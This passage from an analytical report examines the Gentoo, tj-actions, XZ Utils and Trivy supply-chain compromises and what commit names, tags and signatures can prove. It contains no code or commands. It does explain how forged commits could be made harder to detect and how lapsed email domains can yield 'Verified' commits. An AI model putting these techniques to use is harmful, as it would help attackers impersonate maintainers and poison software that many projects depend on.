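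In the 2018 attack on Gentoo, the account used was what misled people. The attacker logged in to GitHub with a real administrator's valid login details, and everything they did afterwards was within that administrator's permissions. The author field hardly misled anyone. A bug report that a user filed during the attack shows the commits under the name "Your Name", a placeholder familiar from Git setup instructions (Gentoo, 2018).

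The attacker also replaced the entire history of `gentoo/gentoo` with a single commit, force-pushed at 20:55, and a minute later put the same commit on `gentoo/musl`, a different repository. Someone who first copied either repository that night would have seen no sign of any earlier commits. People with older copies would have noticed the break when they next updated, which Gentoo listed among the ways it had been lucky.

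The attack was discovered quickly because the attacker removed everyone. GitHub emails people who lose their membership. The first such email went out at 20:26, and by 20:29, ten minutes after the login, a developer had noticed the problem. Gentoo judged that a quieter attacker with the same password would probably have gone unnoticed for much longer.

Gentoo's staff identified the account at 23:40, three hours and 21 minutes after the login and five minutes after GitHub gave them back limited access to the organisation. GitHub had locked the suspected account at 22:45 without telling Gentoo, whose staff learned of this only the next day from the account's security log. Once they had identified the account, GitHub's audit logs helped them reconstruct the sequence of events.

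Those logs were incomplete. At 20:25, the minute the attacker began removing people, Gentoo's automatic copying program pushed one last genuine commit to `gentoo/gentoo`. According to the incident report, that commit is missing from the organisation's audit log. An investigator who trusted only that log might have mistaken the commit for part of the attack. Gentoo could confirm that the commit was genuine because its own servers, which the attacker had never reached, also had it, as an announcement by Gentoo (2018) explained on the second day.

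The third repository the attacker altered, `gentoo/systemd`, existed only on GitHub. Gentoo's staff restored all three by force-push between 06:57 and 06:59 the next morning. Until then, people could still download the malicious versions through Git, because GitHub had hidden the organisation's web pages but had not blocked Git access. The malicious version of `gentoo/gentoo` was available for ten hours and 20 minutes.

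GitHub closed all of Gentoo's past pull requests and disconnected them from their commits, and it could not repair the damage. Projects often depend on pull requests to show who reviewed a change. The attacker failed to destroy Gentoo's commits, but the commits do not show who reviewed them.

### Moved tags at tj-actions

GitHub Actions is a service that runs automated jobs, such as tests, when something in a repository changes. Developers build these jobs from ready-made components called actions, each with its own repository. More than 23,000 repositories used the action tj-actions/changed-files, which lists the files a change affects. Developers can specify an action's version by tag, for example `v45`, and GitHub then runs whichever commit that tag points to when the job runs.

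On 14 March 2025, at 16:57:45 UTC, an attacker moved the tags of the GitHub action changed-files to a malicious commit whose hash begins with 0e58ed8. Esler (2025), in *tj-action/changed-files GitHub action was compromised*, counted 361 tags and described them as all of the action's versions, but Varun Sharma (2025), in *Harden-Runner detection*, wrote that most had moved. Jobs set to use different versions, such as 5 and 44, now ran the same code, which searched the machine's memory for passwords and tokens and printed them in the job's log. Anyone can read those logs if the repository is public.

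The records were false in two places. The tags kept their old names, so each appeared to mark a release that might be years old. The commit also appeared to come from Renovate, a program that proposes updates to the outside software a project uses. The commit's title, "chore(deps): lock file maintenance (#2460)", is typical of Renovate's routine changes.

The attacker had write access through a token stolen from `@tj-actions-bot`, an account the maintainer used for automated work. *GitHub Actions Supply Chain Attack*, by the security company Palo Alto Networks' research team, Unit 42, traces that theft back through two other projects. In December 2024 the attacker stole a token from a maintainer of SpotBugs, a program that looks for errors in Java code. The attacker left it unused for three months, then on 11 March 2025 used it to give a throwaway account write access to SpotBugs. That account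 pushed a new branch and deleted it within a second, but the push still started an automated job that exposed the token of another developer, who also worked on the reviewdog project. With this second token, the attacker moved one tag of a reviewdog action for an hour and 49 minutes. A job at tj-actions ran that action and exposed the bot's token.

At every step, GitHub received a valid token for an account with the necessary rights. Even a perfect push log for the last step would have shown only `@tj-actions-bot` as the pusher.

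#### Was the malicious commit merged?

Published accounts disagree about how the commit got into the repository. According to Unit 42's main account, the attacker added it to a genuine pull request from Renovate, and the pull request then merged automatically under the repository's settings. If so, an automatic approval let the malicious code onto a branch, in the history that maintainers normally read.

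Renovate's author disagreed in *Tj-actions/changed-files GitHub Action Compromised*, a discussion on the programmers' forum Hacker News. The comment there said the attacker had tried to make the change less conspicuous by imitating the repository's most recent commit, which really had come from Renovate. It added that the imitation was not on any branch and that nobody had to be tricked into merging it. Renovate's author was writing partly from memory, because GitHub had already taken the repository down, and had a reason to defend the program. But Sharma, whose company StepSecurity detected the attack, also wrote that the attacker had created the commit outside the repository. *Triaging Action Uses Imposter Commit*, a later StepSecurity guide, places the commit on a fork that nobody ever merged.

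The false commit that seemed to belong to `actions/checkout` shows that an attacker can do this without a merge. Bachmeyer (2025), replying to Esler on a security mailing list, thought it obvious that this commit had also come in through the storage GitHub shares between a repository and its forks. If so, the attacker needed write access only to move the tags.

The commit's title may explain the other version. When GitHub combines a pull request's commits into one and merges the result, it adds a number such as "(#2460)" to the title. Because the attacker had copied the title with its number, anyone who looked up 2460 would have found a real pull request by the real Renovate. The attacker's commit had no signature, though GitHub signs the commits it creates in such merges. Renovate also added to the confusion by opening genuine pull requests during the attack that would update other people's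 repositories to the malicious version. Some of those repositories merged them automatically.

Unit 42's later update, of 2 April 2025, supports the version without a merge, because its summary and timeline mention only the moved tags. None of these accounts lists the repository's branches as they were that afternoon, which would settle the question, but the evidence that the commit was on no branch is much stronger than the evidence that it was merged.

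An investigator would look for different evidence depending on which version they believed. A merge would have left a pull request, an approval or a setting that removed the need for one, and a new commit on the main branch, but moving a tag leaves none of these. If a company's AI service loaded its safety configuration from a tag, an attacker could change the blocking threshold by moving the tag, while every commit on the main branch still showed the old value.

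#### How people found out

StepSecurity sells a tool that monitors the network connections of automated jobs. The tool raised an alert when the malicious code downloaded a script from an address that the action had never contacted before. The timing of the alert is uncertain. Sharma's post puts the start of the attack at about 16:00 UTC and the first confirmation at 17:00, but Esler and Unit 42 both say the tags moved at 16:57, which would leave three minutes to investigate. The next entry in the post, at 20:00, reports that public repositories were leaking passwords and tokens, so the discovery took about three hours at most.

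The earlier steps stayed hidden for longer. The reviewdog tag moved on 11 March, and the researcher Adnan Khan drew attention to it on 16 March, after the larger attack had given people a reason to look. Unit 42 explained the theft of the SpotBugs token almost four months after it happened. It also found that GitHub did not record tag changes in the audit logs of organisations on its free plan. The accounts used to prepare the attack had disappeared from GitHub, but the commits from one deleted fork were still available through the original reviewdog repository, because the shared storage that had let the attacker hide the code's origin also preserved them.

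Wiz's *GitHub Action tj-actions/changed-files supply chain attack* (2025) argues that the missing "Verified" badge shows that nobody had taken over Renovate's account. This is probably right, since the real bot signs its commits, but the missing badge alone doesn't prove it, because an intruder with the bot's login details could also have pushed an unsigned commit. The better evidence is that the maintainers identified a different stolen token that was enough for the whole attack.

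The US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) advised users to check the period from midnight on 12 March to noon on 15 March, UTC, which was much longer than the attack on the tags had lasted (*Supply Chain Compromise of Third-Party tj-actions/changed-files*, 2025). The caution was reasonable, because Unit 42 found that the attacker had prepared a separate malicious version for a single target, the cryptocurrency company Coinbase. Coinbase had run it at 15:10 on 14 March, nearly two hours before the mass change. That version carried yet another false name, `github-actions[bot]`.

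A moved tag is weak evidence of an attack on its own, because maintainers also move or delete tags for reasons such as correcting a faulty release or tidying up a repository. *Mutating the "Immutable"* (Rapaport, Pautet and colleagues, 2026) compared successive archived copies of public repositories and found about 10.2 million cases in which someone had moved or deleted a tag. These were in 188,713 repositories, or 0.41% of those the team could check. Of 626,008 tags that had moved, 68% pointed to different file contents afterwards. The team could see the changes only because the archive had kept the repositories' earlier state.

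StepSecurity now looks for a narrower sign, a commit that jobs use but that isn't on any branch of the action's repository. This can also happen innocently, for instance when maintainers create a temporary branch for a release, tag the commit and then delete the branch.

### A trusted maintainer at XZ Utils

In these three attacks, somebody used a name or an account that belonged to someone else. The backdoor in XZ Utils, however, came from the account listed in the records, and the account's owner had the right to use it. *Wolves in the Repository* (Przymus and Durieux, 2025) reconstructs the attack from 1,020 commits, 2,944 GitHub events and 307 mailing-list messages, but doesn't name the people involved.

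XZ Utils is part of many Linux systems, and one person had maintained it since 2009. The attacker first appeared on 29 October 2021, and in 2022 contributed code and gained write access to the repository. In May and June 2022, accounts that were probably fake posted to the project's mailing list to support the attacker's aims. In 2023 the attacker took over most of the maintenance work, including translations and the system that builds and tests the software. All of this work was useful to the project, and the version history recorded it correctly.

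The malicious work followed in early 2024. The backdoor affected OpenSSH, the program that many servers use for remote logins. It let someone with a particular private key run commands on a server before logging in, or log in with any password. OpenSSH does not use XZ Utils, but several Linux distributions had modified it in a way that loaded the XZ library.

Part of the attack was missing from the repository. The harmful code was in a binary file disguised as test data, and such files are normal in a project that has to test compressed files. A change to the build scripts extracted the code and added it to the finished library, but that change appeared only in the packages the attacker prepared by hand for each release. Someone who read every line of text in the Git repository would not have found the instructions that activated the backdoor. Przymus and Durieux write that the attacker never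 pushed malicious code, which is true only if the test file isn't counted as malicious code.

Comparing the release package with the repository could have revealed the extra script, just as comparing the two copies of `exit.c` revealed the false revisions in 2003. But BitMover's two copies were supposed to be identical, so any difference signaled a problem. Release packages normally contain files that are not in Git, added by the tools that prepare them, so one more attracted no attention. The same could happen with an AI safeguard if a company's build process routinely adds or rewrites settings. The repository could then show a threshold of 0.50 while the servers used another value.

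A PostgreSQL developer at Microsoft found the backdoor on 28 March 2024. He had noticed that OpenSSH was using an unusual amount of processor time during logins and traced the problem to XZ Utils. Przymus and Durieux credit the discovery to luck as well as persistence. The attacker had first appeared two years and five months earlier (Przymus and Durieux give 2.6 years, which doesn't fit their own dates), but the malicious activity was less than three months old.

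In his announcement, the discoverer considered whether the account's owner was directly involved or somebody had thoroughly compromised the owner's computer. He thought a compromise was unlikely because the activity had gone on for several weeks and the owner had written publicly about supposed fixes for problems the backdoor caused. An intruder would have had to keep this up for weeks without the owner noticing. This is a good argument for linking the actions to whoever normally used the account, but it does not establish that person's identity.

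The history also doesn't show what other contributors intended. On 22 June 2023 the project accepted a change that let the library choose between versions of a function when a program starts. The stated purpose was a small gain in speed, but the backdoor later depended on this change. It came from another account, which made only a few contributions and then became inactive. Przymus and Durieux say it is still unclear whether the person behind the account was improving the software in good faith or preparing the attack.

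### What failed in each case

These compromises usually involve several failures. The tj-actions attacker, for example, used a false name, used a stolen token and moved tags. The table therefore lists each case under the failure that misled people most. Nobody discovered any of the four attacks by checking the names on commits.

| What failed | Case | What the records suggested | What exposed the attack | Time to discovery |
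|---|---|---|---|---|
| The name | Linux, 2003 | David Miller had edited `exit.c` | Nightly comparison with the main repository | About 20 or 28 hours, depending on the log's time zone |
| The account | Gentoo, 2018 | An administrator had removed colleagues and replaced the history | Emails to the removed developers | 10 minutes, and 3 hours 21 minutes to identify the account |
| The reference | tj-actions, 2025 | Old version tags still pointed to old releases | An unexpected network connection | About 3 hours at most |
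| Trust in the person | XZ Utils, 2024 | A trusted maintainer was doing routine work | Unusually high processor use during logins | Less than 3 months after the malicious work began |

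## How were the forged Trivy releases of 2026 made to look old?

Trivy is a free program that checks software for known security flaws. The company Aqua Security maintains it and two GitHub actions, trivy-action and setup-trivy, which other projects use to run or install it automatically. More than 10,000 automated job files on GitHub refer to trivy-action, according to *Trivy Under Attack Again* (Burckhardt, 2026). On 19 March 2026, an attacker moved almost all of trivy-action's version tags to commits whose code stole passwords and tokens from the machines that ran it.

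The Trivy attacker moved each old tag to its own new commit, and copied in the names, dates and message of the commit that the tag had pointed to before. Someone who looked up an old version in the log would have seen the entry they expected, with its original date. The tj-actions attacker had also moved old tags, but pointed them all to one commit with one false name.

### The stolen service account

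The attacker worked through `aqua-bot`, a service account, which programs use for routine jobs such as publishing releases. In late February, someone had exploited a misconfigured job in Trivy's repository and copied the account's access token. In *Trivy Compromised a Second Time*, Sharma (2026) attributes the theft to hackerbot-claw, an automated attack program active on 28 February. In *20 Days Later*, Proulx (2026) dates the theft to 27 February and thinks hackerbot-claw only tested the token. At least 33 automated jobs in Aqua's GitHub organisation used the token, which seems to have given write access to several repositories.

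Aqua disclosed the theft on 1 March and replaced its passwords and tokens. Its GitHub advisory, *Trivy ecosystem supply chain was briefly compromised* (2026), says that this took a few days and that the old ones did not all stop working at the same time. The attacker could have copied the new ones using an old token that still worked.

This explanation is plausible, but Aqua has not published the evidence for it. Proulx first reported that Aqua had never replaced `aqua-bot`'s token, but withdrew the claim after another researcher noticed that a scheduled job using the token had failed six times in a row between 28 February and 1 March and then worked again. One would expect that pattern if somebody had replaced the token. Proulx's corrected article leaves open how the attacker got back in.

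### A new commit behind each old tag

Burckhardt reconstructed how the attacker altered trivy-action. For each tag, the attacker copied the original commit's author, committer, both dates and full message, including the pull request number. Every forged commit had the same files, taken from the newest version of the action with one script replaced, and the same parent, the newest commit on the main branch. The forged commits differed only in the copied names, dates and messages. The attacker then force-pushed each tag to point to its forged commit. The altered script stole the passwords and then ran the real scan, so the job's output looked normal too.

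Aqua's GitHub advisory says the attacker moved 76 of 77 tags, while Burckhardt and Proulx say 75 of 76. In both counts, only the newest tag, 0.35.0, was untouched. Burckhardt lists 75 altered tags with their hashes, and Sharma's table also has 75. The advisory gives only a range, 0.0.1 to 0.34.2. OSV's *Trivy ecosystem supply chain briefly compromised* (2026), an entry in a public database of security flaws, repeats Aqua's figure, but its list of versions seems to come from the scanner's repository, not the action's.

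Aqua's longer account, *Ongoing Investigation and Continued Remediation* (2026), gives the number of altered tags as 76 in its own timeline and 75 in the passages it took from Burckhardt's company, Socket. Aqua may have counted a tag that outside researchers missed, or someone may have miscounted. Nobody seems to have published the name or hash of a 76th altered tag, so outsiders can check only 75.

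The attacker also replaced all seven tags of setup-trivy. One of the forged commits copied the message of the newest genuine commit, "Pin Trivy install script checkout to a specific commit (#28)". According to ramimac.me's *Trivy Supply Chain Compromise* (2026), it also had the name of the contributor Tomochika Hara and a date of 15 January 2026. Sharma found that the genuine commit added four lines, while the forged one added 117 and removed 12. The attacker had made the genuine commit the parent of the forged one, so the log showed the same message twice in a row.

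### Two forged commits behind a new release

On the same day, the attacker published v0.69.4, a malicious new version of the scanner itself, using two more forged commits. One was the commit in Guillermo Rauch's name that seemed to belong to `actions/checkout`, the action that most automated jobs use to fetch a repository's files. The forged version also fetched the attacker's source code.

The other commit named DmitriyLewen, a real Trivy maintainer, as its author and had the message "fix(ci): Use correct checkout pinning". It made Trivy's release job use the false checkout commit, identified by its full hash. Security guides recommend identifying code this way because a hash always refers to the same code. According to Proulx, the commit also switched off a check on the finished release and changed quotation marks throughout the file to make the important changes harder for a reviewer to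 spot.

At 17:43:37 UTC the attacker pushed a v0.69.4 tag that pointed to this commit, and Trivy's automated job built and published the release. The malicious program code was never in the tagged source. Homebrew, which distributes software for Mac and Linux, compiled the program from source and so got a clean copy, although Proulx at first reported that it had passed on the backdoor.

Nobody merged either commit into the main branch of the repository it seemed to belong to. GitHub still displays such a commit under the repository's address, with a warning that it "does not belong to any branch on this repository". susam.codeberg.page's *Accessing Fork Commits via Original Repository* reports a small test in which Codeberg, another code-hosting site, returned a page-not-found error instead.

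People who read only the job's settings don't see that warning, and GitHub Actions still runs these commits, which Chainguard's *What the fork?* calls imposter commits. Even specialists reading about this attack could be misled, because a list of warning signs in Sharma's post describes both the false `actions/checkout` commit and the setup-trivy commit as legitimate, although the post explains elsewhere that the setup-trivy commit stole passwords.

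The evidence that these commits came from forks is weaker. GitHub warns only that a commit "may belong to a fork", and an attacker with write access can also push a commit directly along with a tag. ramimac.me points to a GitHub account, created on 10 March and since deleted, whose only public activity was forking Trivy and `actions/checkout`. This is consistent with those two commits coming from forks, but nobody has shown that the account belonged to the attacker.

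*GitHub Actions is the weakest link* (2026) proposes that GitHub refuse to run a commit unless it is on a branch of the official repository. An attacker would then have to push malicious code to a branch, where maintainers are more likely to see it. The attack technique still worked after the Trivy attack. The Hacker News' *Popular GitHub Action Tags Redirected to Imposter Commit to Steal CI/CD Credentials* reports that someone later moved every tag of the action `actions-cool/issues-helper` to an imposter commit.

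### What gave the backdating away

Burckhardt found four inconsistencies in the altered trivy-action versions. GitHub had signed the original commits when maintainers merged them on its website, but the copies had no signature. The copies were dated 2021, 2022 and other past years, although their parent commit was from March 2026. Each copy changed only one file, while the originals had usually changed several. GitHub's page for each altered release showed "0 commits to master since this release" (master is the main branch), but an old version such as 0.6.0 should have had hundreds.

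Three of these signs appeared because the attacker built every forged commit on the newest commit, probably so that one altered script would work for every tag. A more patient forger could have started from each original commit's parent and files and fitted the malicious code to dozens of old versions of the script. The dates would then have been in a believable order, and the list of changed files would have looked much more like the original.

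Even the release page would have been almost right. It counts the commits on the main branch that are missing from the tag's history. If a forged commit replaced the original but kept the original's parent, the original would be missing too, so the count would be one too high, which only someone who knew the correct number would notice.

| Sign | Could a more careful forger remove it? |
|---|---|
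| Date years older than the parent's | Yes, by using the original's parent |
| Only one changed file | Largely, by starting from the original's files, though the script would still differ |
| No later commits on the release page | Almost, leaving the counter wrong by one |
| Commit on no branch | Yes, by pushing it to a branch, which would make it easier to find |
| Missing GitHub signature | Not by copying the original signature, which fits only the original contents |
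| Different commit hash | No, but the change is visible only to someone who has the old hash |

The missing signature was a useful clue because the originals had one. In a project that doesn't sign its commits, an unsigned copy would look no different from the rest.

The old hash is the most reliable evidence, and the attacker could not erase it from other people's computers. Projects that specify an action by hash often note the version next to it, and programs such as Renovate open a request to update the hash when the tag moves. The Eclipse Foundation's *Don't become the next Trivy* advises reviewers to be suspicious when such a request changes the hash but not the version. Sharma describes one in the open-source project k8gb. It recorded that the trivy-action tag had moved, but the project's automated job then ran the malicious commit before anyone investigated.

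The same evidence would matter in a dispute over an AI safeguard. Suppose a company's tag for its June 2025 safety configuration now points to a commit dated June 2025, containing a file that sets the blocking threshold to 0.90. Someone could have made that commit last week and backdated it. To find out whether the threshold was 0.90 in June 2025, an investigator would need an older copy of the repository or a deployment record with the hash that the company used then.

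Aqua could offer better evidence for the age of some genuine Trivy files. Its advisory explains how to check the signature on the v0.69.2 program file against a public log. The log added its own time for the signing, 1 March, which was 18 days before the attack.

### The "Immutable" badge

GitHub showed the word "Immutable" beside the altered releases, which made them look more trustworthy. According to GitHub's *Immutable releases*, nobody can change an immutable release's files or move its tag after publication. When the feature became generally available in October 2025, GitHub's *Immutable releases are now generally available* (2025) explained that existing releases would stay changeable unless their owners republished them. Aqua turned the feature on for trivy-action on 4 March 2026, but this did not protect the versions it had already published.

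Burckhardt suggests that the attacker moved the old tags and then deliberately published the releases as immutable, which locked the malicious commits in place. According to Aqua's advisory, the force-push itself caused GitHub to treat the releases as immutable. In either case, the badge meant only that nobody had changed the release since the lock took effect, which could have been that same day. The lock also prevented Aqua from reusing the altered tags' names after deleting them, so it had to publish the genuine versions under new ones, such as v0.34.0 instead of 0.34.0.

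Sources give two reasons why 0.35.0 was not replaced. Eclipse Foundation and Aqua's advisory say that it was already immutable. Burckhardt thinks the attacker's program skipped it because it pointed to the parent of all the forged commits, and that a replacement would have been its own parent. That last point is wrong, because changing the script would have produced a new commit with a different hash and an ordinary parent. That commit might even have been the most convincing forgery, since the dates would have matched. The attacker may still have avoided the newest release for fear of attention, but immutability is enough to explain why it survived. Aqua Security gives both reasons in different parts of its account. It also warns that the badge "does not prevent tag force-pushing", which is hard to reconcile with its claim that immutability protected 0.35.0.

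Immutable releases protect old releases but do not stop anyone with the right token from adding a new one. Aqua had turned the feature on for the scanner on 3 March, and the attacker still published v0.69.4 there. The Eclipse Foundation is therefore wrong to say that the attacker could have done nothing useful with the stolen credentials if every tag had been immutable.

### Gaps in the public record

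GitHub publishes a feed of events in open repositories, and researchers use archived copies of it to reconstruct attacks, but the most important events of 19 March are missing. Proulx explains that force-pushing an existing tag produces neither a "create" nor a "delete" event in the archived data. Even deletions can be missing. Sharma found an event for a maintainer's removal of the v0.2.5 tag from setup-trivy at 21:07 UTC, but none for v0.2.0 to v0.2.4, which had also disappeared.

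This may be why published times for the tag changes differ by more than four hours. Aqua's longer account puts them at about 17:43 UTC, but a footnote in its advisory gives that as the time of the earliest suspicious activity in its audit log. Sharma gives about 18:45, and ramimac.me gives 22:08. The 22:08 time is too late for the first changes, because Socket's alerts about the malicious actions began at 19:15. The tags probably moved between 17:43 and 19:15, and Aqua could presumably narrow this down from its log.

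The feed shows `aqua-bot` deleting a tag called v0.70.0 at 17:51:17, which is hard to explain. Proulx thinks the attacker tried that version number first and then fell back on v0.69.4, but the v0.69.4 tag had already been up for nearly eight minutes when the deletion happened. According to Aqua's advisory, the attacker put malicious code on a branch called v0.70.0 and never pushed a tag of that name, which contradicts the feed. ramimac.me notes that the commit behind the deleted tag was dated 16 March and suggests that the attacker may have controlled `aqua-bot` by then. That is possible, but the attacker could have forged this date too.

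The attacker also removed part of the discussion about the attack. Users had been sharing evidence about v0.69.4 in the GitHub thread where Aqua had disclosed the February breach, until `aqua-bot` deleted the thread. At 22:13 someone opened a new thread to ask where the old one had gone, and a user who had copied some of the technical details posted them there. Shortly after midnight, dozens of accounts flooded the new thread with empty praise such as "worked perfectly for me". Sharma counted at least 17 such comments in one second, Proulx counted 47 accounts in twelve seconds, and ramimac.me counted 96 in about half a minute.

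Two accounts also posted a taunt naming TeamPCP, a known criminal group, and a comment in the malicious code contained the same name. Burckhardt considers the attribution to TeamPCP plausible because the code resembles the group's earlier tools, but warns that the name could have been planted to mislead.

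## What does a signature on a commit prove?

Nobody can sign new contents without the private key, so a signature is better evidence than an author field. Missing signatures helped expose the forged Trivy versions. An investigator still has to find out who used the key and whether they were allowed to.

### How signing and verification work

Each private key has a matching public key, which its owner can give to anyone. Write m for the text of a commit without its signature. Signing takes three steps:

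1. Git assembles m.
2. A signing program computes the signature, s = Sign(private key, m).
3. Git inserts s after the committer line and computes the commit hash from the whole text, h = H(m, s).

Verification takes four:

1. Git takes s out of the commit, which leaves m.
2. The verifier's software looks for the public key. A signature in the OpenPGP format, which most signers make with the program GPG, gives only the key's identifier, so the verifier needs a copy of the key. A signature made with an SSH key contains the public key itself.
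3. The software computes Verify(public key, m, s), which accepts or rejects the signature. If anyone has changed a single character of m, it rejects.
4. The verifier decides whose key it is and whether that person's signature counts.

The mathematical part of the check ends at step 3. In a PHP discussion, Rethans (2024) posted Git's output from checking one of his own recent commits. It showed a time, a key identifier and his email addresses, with the word "ultimate" after each address. The word appeared because a setting on his computer marked the key as fully trusted. On a computer without his public key, the same command would have reported that it could not check the signature.

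### What a valid signature leaves open

A valid signature shows that a person or program with access to the private key signed the commit's exact contents. Those contents include the names and dates recorded by the signer's software, and the tree identifier, which covers every file. The names can still be false, since Ben can sign a commit that lists Ana as its author.

The signature doesn't show who used the key. A thief may have copied the key, or malicious software may have used it while it was unlocked on the owner's computer. Many developers set Git to sign every commit automatically. If a coding agent works on the developer's computer under those settings, Git signs the agent's commits with the developer's key, even if the developer never read the changes.

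A signature also doesn't show that the signer had permission to make the change. Checking it gives the same result whether the signer is the head of a safety team, an intern or a stranger. The XZ Utils attacker was a maintainer with permission to commit, so a rule requiring signatures would not have kept them out.

The time of signing is uncertain too. An OpenPGP signature contains a time, but it comes from the signer's computer. An SSH signature contains no time, so Git uses the committer date, which the signer can choose, to check whether the key was valid. Someone who steals an expired key can therefore backdate a commit to a day when the key was still valid. An outside record can at least show that a signed commit existed by a certain time. GitHub, for instance, stores the time when it first verified a commit's signature.

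A commit's signature does not cover the branch or tag that points to the commit. Anyone who could move a company's production tag could point it back to an old commit with a looser threshold, and that commit's signature would still be valid.

### Personal keys, GitHub's key and the "Verified" badge

The signature that GitHub adds to commits made on its website shows that GitHub created the commit for a logged-in session. It is therefore evidence about an account, like an entry in a push log, and is only as reliable as GitHub's login checks and GitHub's own security. Sharma and Kancherla point out that an attacker who controlled the hosting server could alter a change a user made on the website, and the result would still carry a valid platform signature.

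Mockus had to separate personal keys from platform keys to learn about individuals from signatures. Two of the 586,011 keys in his data, both belonging to platforms, account for 95.9% of the links between keys and authors. He treated a key as personal if it had signed for no more than 50 authors. This left 583,360 keys, of which 72% had signed for only one author.

Even these keys don't always identify a person. Mockus looked at 32,192 pairs of author names that shared a key but that an existing name-matching method had treated as different people. In 28% of the pairs, the names or addresses had something in common that suggested one person. He concluded that the rest were two people sharing a key, though some could be one person using a pseudonym. He also looked up a random sample of 398 personal keys on a public server where people publish their keys. He found 78, and only 39 of those listed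 an email address that matched the author's.

Most readers rely on GitHub's "Verified" badge and never look at the key. For a commit signed with a user's own key, the badge means that the signature is valid, the key is registered to a GitHub account, and the committer's email address is a confirmed address on that account. Anyone with an account can meet these conditions for their own commits, whether or not a project trusts them.

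The badge also applies to the committer, not the author. Sharma and Kancherla explain that an attacker can list a victim as the author, sign as committer with the attacker's own key and still get a "Verified" badge. If the victim has turned on vigilant mode, GitHub shows "Partially verified" instead.

An attacker may not need to steal an account to sign commits in someone else's name. Holtgrave, Friedrich and colleagues, in *Attributing Open-Source Contributions is Critical but Difficult* (2025), found 138,743 internet domains in the commit email addresses of 50,328 widely used GitHub projects. Of these domains, 4,107 had no owner. Anyone could register one, receive mail at a former contributor's address, confirm the address on a GitHub account if no other account held it, and add a signing key. GitHub would then show new commits in the former contributor's name as verified.

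According to Ginesin, GitHub permanently stores the result of its first check, so a commit keeps its "Verified" badge even if its owner later revokes the signing key. But a participant in the PHP discussion recalled losing a device that held his key several years earlier, and said that when he revoked the key, GitHub marked every commit he had signed with it as unverified. The two accounts probably describe different periods, since Ginesin was writing in 2026. Under the newer system, the badge shows the result of GitHub's first check, and an investigator has to find out separately whether the owner later reported the key stolen.

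Users can instead check signatures against their own list of keys. Git can read a file that pairs email addresses with the SSH keys allowed to sign for them, and GPG has a similar store of public keys. Users then decide which keys to accept, but they have to collect them first. Holtgrave and colleagues found only about a third of GitHub users' OpenPGP keys on the public key servers they checked, and SSH keys have no such servers. In practice, most people who want to check a stranger's signature have to get the key from GitHub, so they still depend on GitHub to identify its owner.

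### The debate at PHP

On 2 April 2024, a few days after the XZ backdoor became public, Rethans asked whether PHP should require signatures on commits to php-src. Most replies were favourable, and Jakub Zelenka, another PHP developer, said most regular committers already signed their commits. Rowan Tommins had assumed the project had required signatures since its move to GitHub in 2021.

Ilija Tovilo, who also works on PHP, signed his own commits but struggled to see which attack the rule would prevent. Someone who takes over a maintainer's GitHub account can edit files on the website, and GitHub will sign the commits. They can also add their own key to the account. If a developer uses one SSH key for both pushing and signing, a thief who copies it can do both. In his view, the rule would mainly stop a thief who had stolen a key or token for pushing but couldn't get a separate signing key.

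Tommins replied that without signatures, someone who steals one account can forge commits in anyone's name, so a team that discovers the theft has to review every commit in the repository. If every commit needs a signature, the team can search for those made with the stolen key or account. He compared the theft without signatures to cloning the credit card of everyone who enters a shop, rather than stealing one customer's card. Zelenka thought it even more important that signatures would show the team whose access to revoke.

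Tovilo agreed that both points were fair. He had wanted to draw attention to other measures, such as allowing only release managers to push to release branches, or requiring a second person to approve each change. He was arguing about how to prevent attacks, whereas Tommins and Zelenka were mostly concerned with what happens after one. Their argument matters more to someone trying to establish who changed a file.

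A signature proves less than Tommins made it sound. He wrote that a compromised account could sign only under its own identity. The account is limited to its own key, but the signer can still name someone else as the author, and GitHub may still display the "Verified" badge. The damage is limited to one identity only if investigators search by key and ignore the names. By 2024, GitHub's push records could also have identified the account, but unlike those records, a signature is in every copy of the repository.

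Tommins also described the 2021 breach as direct write access to the server, the explanation that Popov had withdrawn. An intruder in control of the server could have turned off any signature check there, although developers could still have noticed the missing signatures in their own copies of the repository. But the attacker actually used password logins, so a server that accepted only commits signed with keys already on file would have refused both commits, unless the same passwords had also let the attacker register a new key.

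Tim Düsterhus suggested that signatures can also help in an investigation. If a developer who always signs with one key suddenly uses another, or if a single commit is signed with a different key from the rest, the team knows where to look first. If the developer keeps a separate key on each computer, the signature may even show which computer the attacker compromised.

Participants also disagreed about how anyone would know who owned a key. Rethans preferred OpenPGP because its users can check one another's identity and then sign one another's keys, creating a "web of trust". Several developers had signed his key. But neither GitHub nor Git's own command shows these endorsements, and GitHub cannot require OpenPGP signatures while refusing SSH ones. Düsterhus considered the web of trust effectively dead and thought a key could gain a reputation from the good commits signed with it. That would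 help with long-standing contributors, but the XZ attacker built up this kind of reputation.

### Does PHP require signatures now?

Rethans ended the discussion by announcing a short formal proposal to require signatures on all branches. There is no sign that he submitted it or that PHP's developers voted on one. The contributor guide shipped with PHP 8.4.16 lists rules for people with push access and does not mention signatures. This is weak evidence, because the guide is outdated (it still describes version 8.4 as under development) and PHP could have turned on the requirement in GitHub's settings without documenting it. On the public evidence, PHP encourages signing but has not adopted a rule requiring it.

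Many of its commits have a signature anyway. In a May 2026 discussion started by Udaltsov, Tovilo explained that developers merge most pull requests for the main branch on GitHub's website, where GitHub signs the result. Bug fixes have to go into several versions, and developers handle these by hand. This usually involves rebasing, or recreating a commit on top of a different parent. The parent's hash is part of m, so the contributor's original signature no longer matches the commit. The new commit is signed only if the developer who recreated it signs it.

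Other projects have run into the same problem, including OpenBao, which makes software for storing passwords and keys. A rebase changes the signed text, so no software could preserve the original signatures. GitHub could at most add a new signature of its own. OpenBao's proposal, *signed commits*, instead attributes the invalid signatures to a GitHub bug. It proposes to stop requiring signatures from occasional contributors and keep the rule for core maintainers.

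The automation project Ansible took a similar approach, as a forum thread under its *IMPORTANT* notice shows. It required signed commits in its main GitHub organisation but exempted two others after contributors described cases it had not foreseen. One developer realised that the rule would affect his bot because he had not yet added commit signing, which he had been meaning to do for more than five years.

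### How many developers sign?

Four studies have measured signing on a large scale, and their headline figures range from 15.7% to 44% of commits.

| Study | Commits examined | Signed commits | Without GitHub's own signatures |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mockus | 5.87 billion in a public archive | 17.59% | Not given for commits; 0.74% of authors have a personal key |
| Holtgrave and colleagues | 25.9 million in 50,328 widely used projects | 15.7% | 5.0% |
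| Sharma and Kancherla | 869,437 in 60 popular repositories, 2020–2024 | 33.27% | 9.65%, also leaving out bots |
| Zhang and colleagues | 12.5 million from active contributors, summer 2022 | 44% | Not given |

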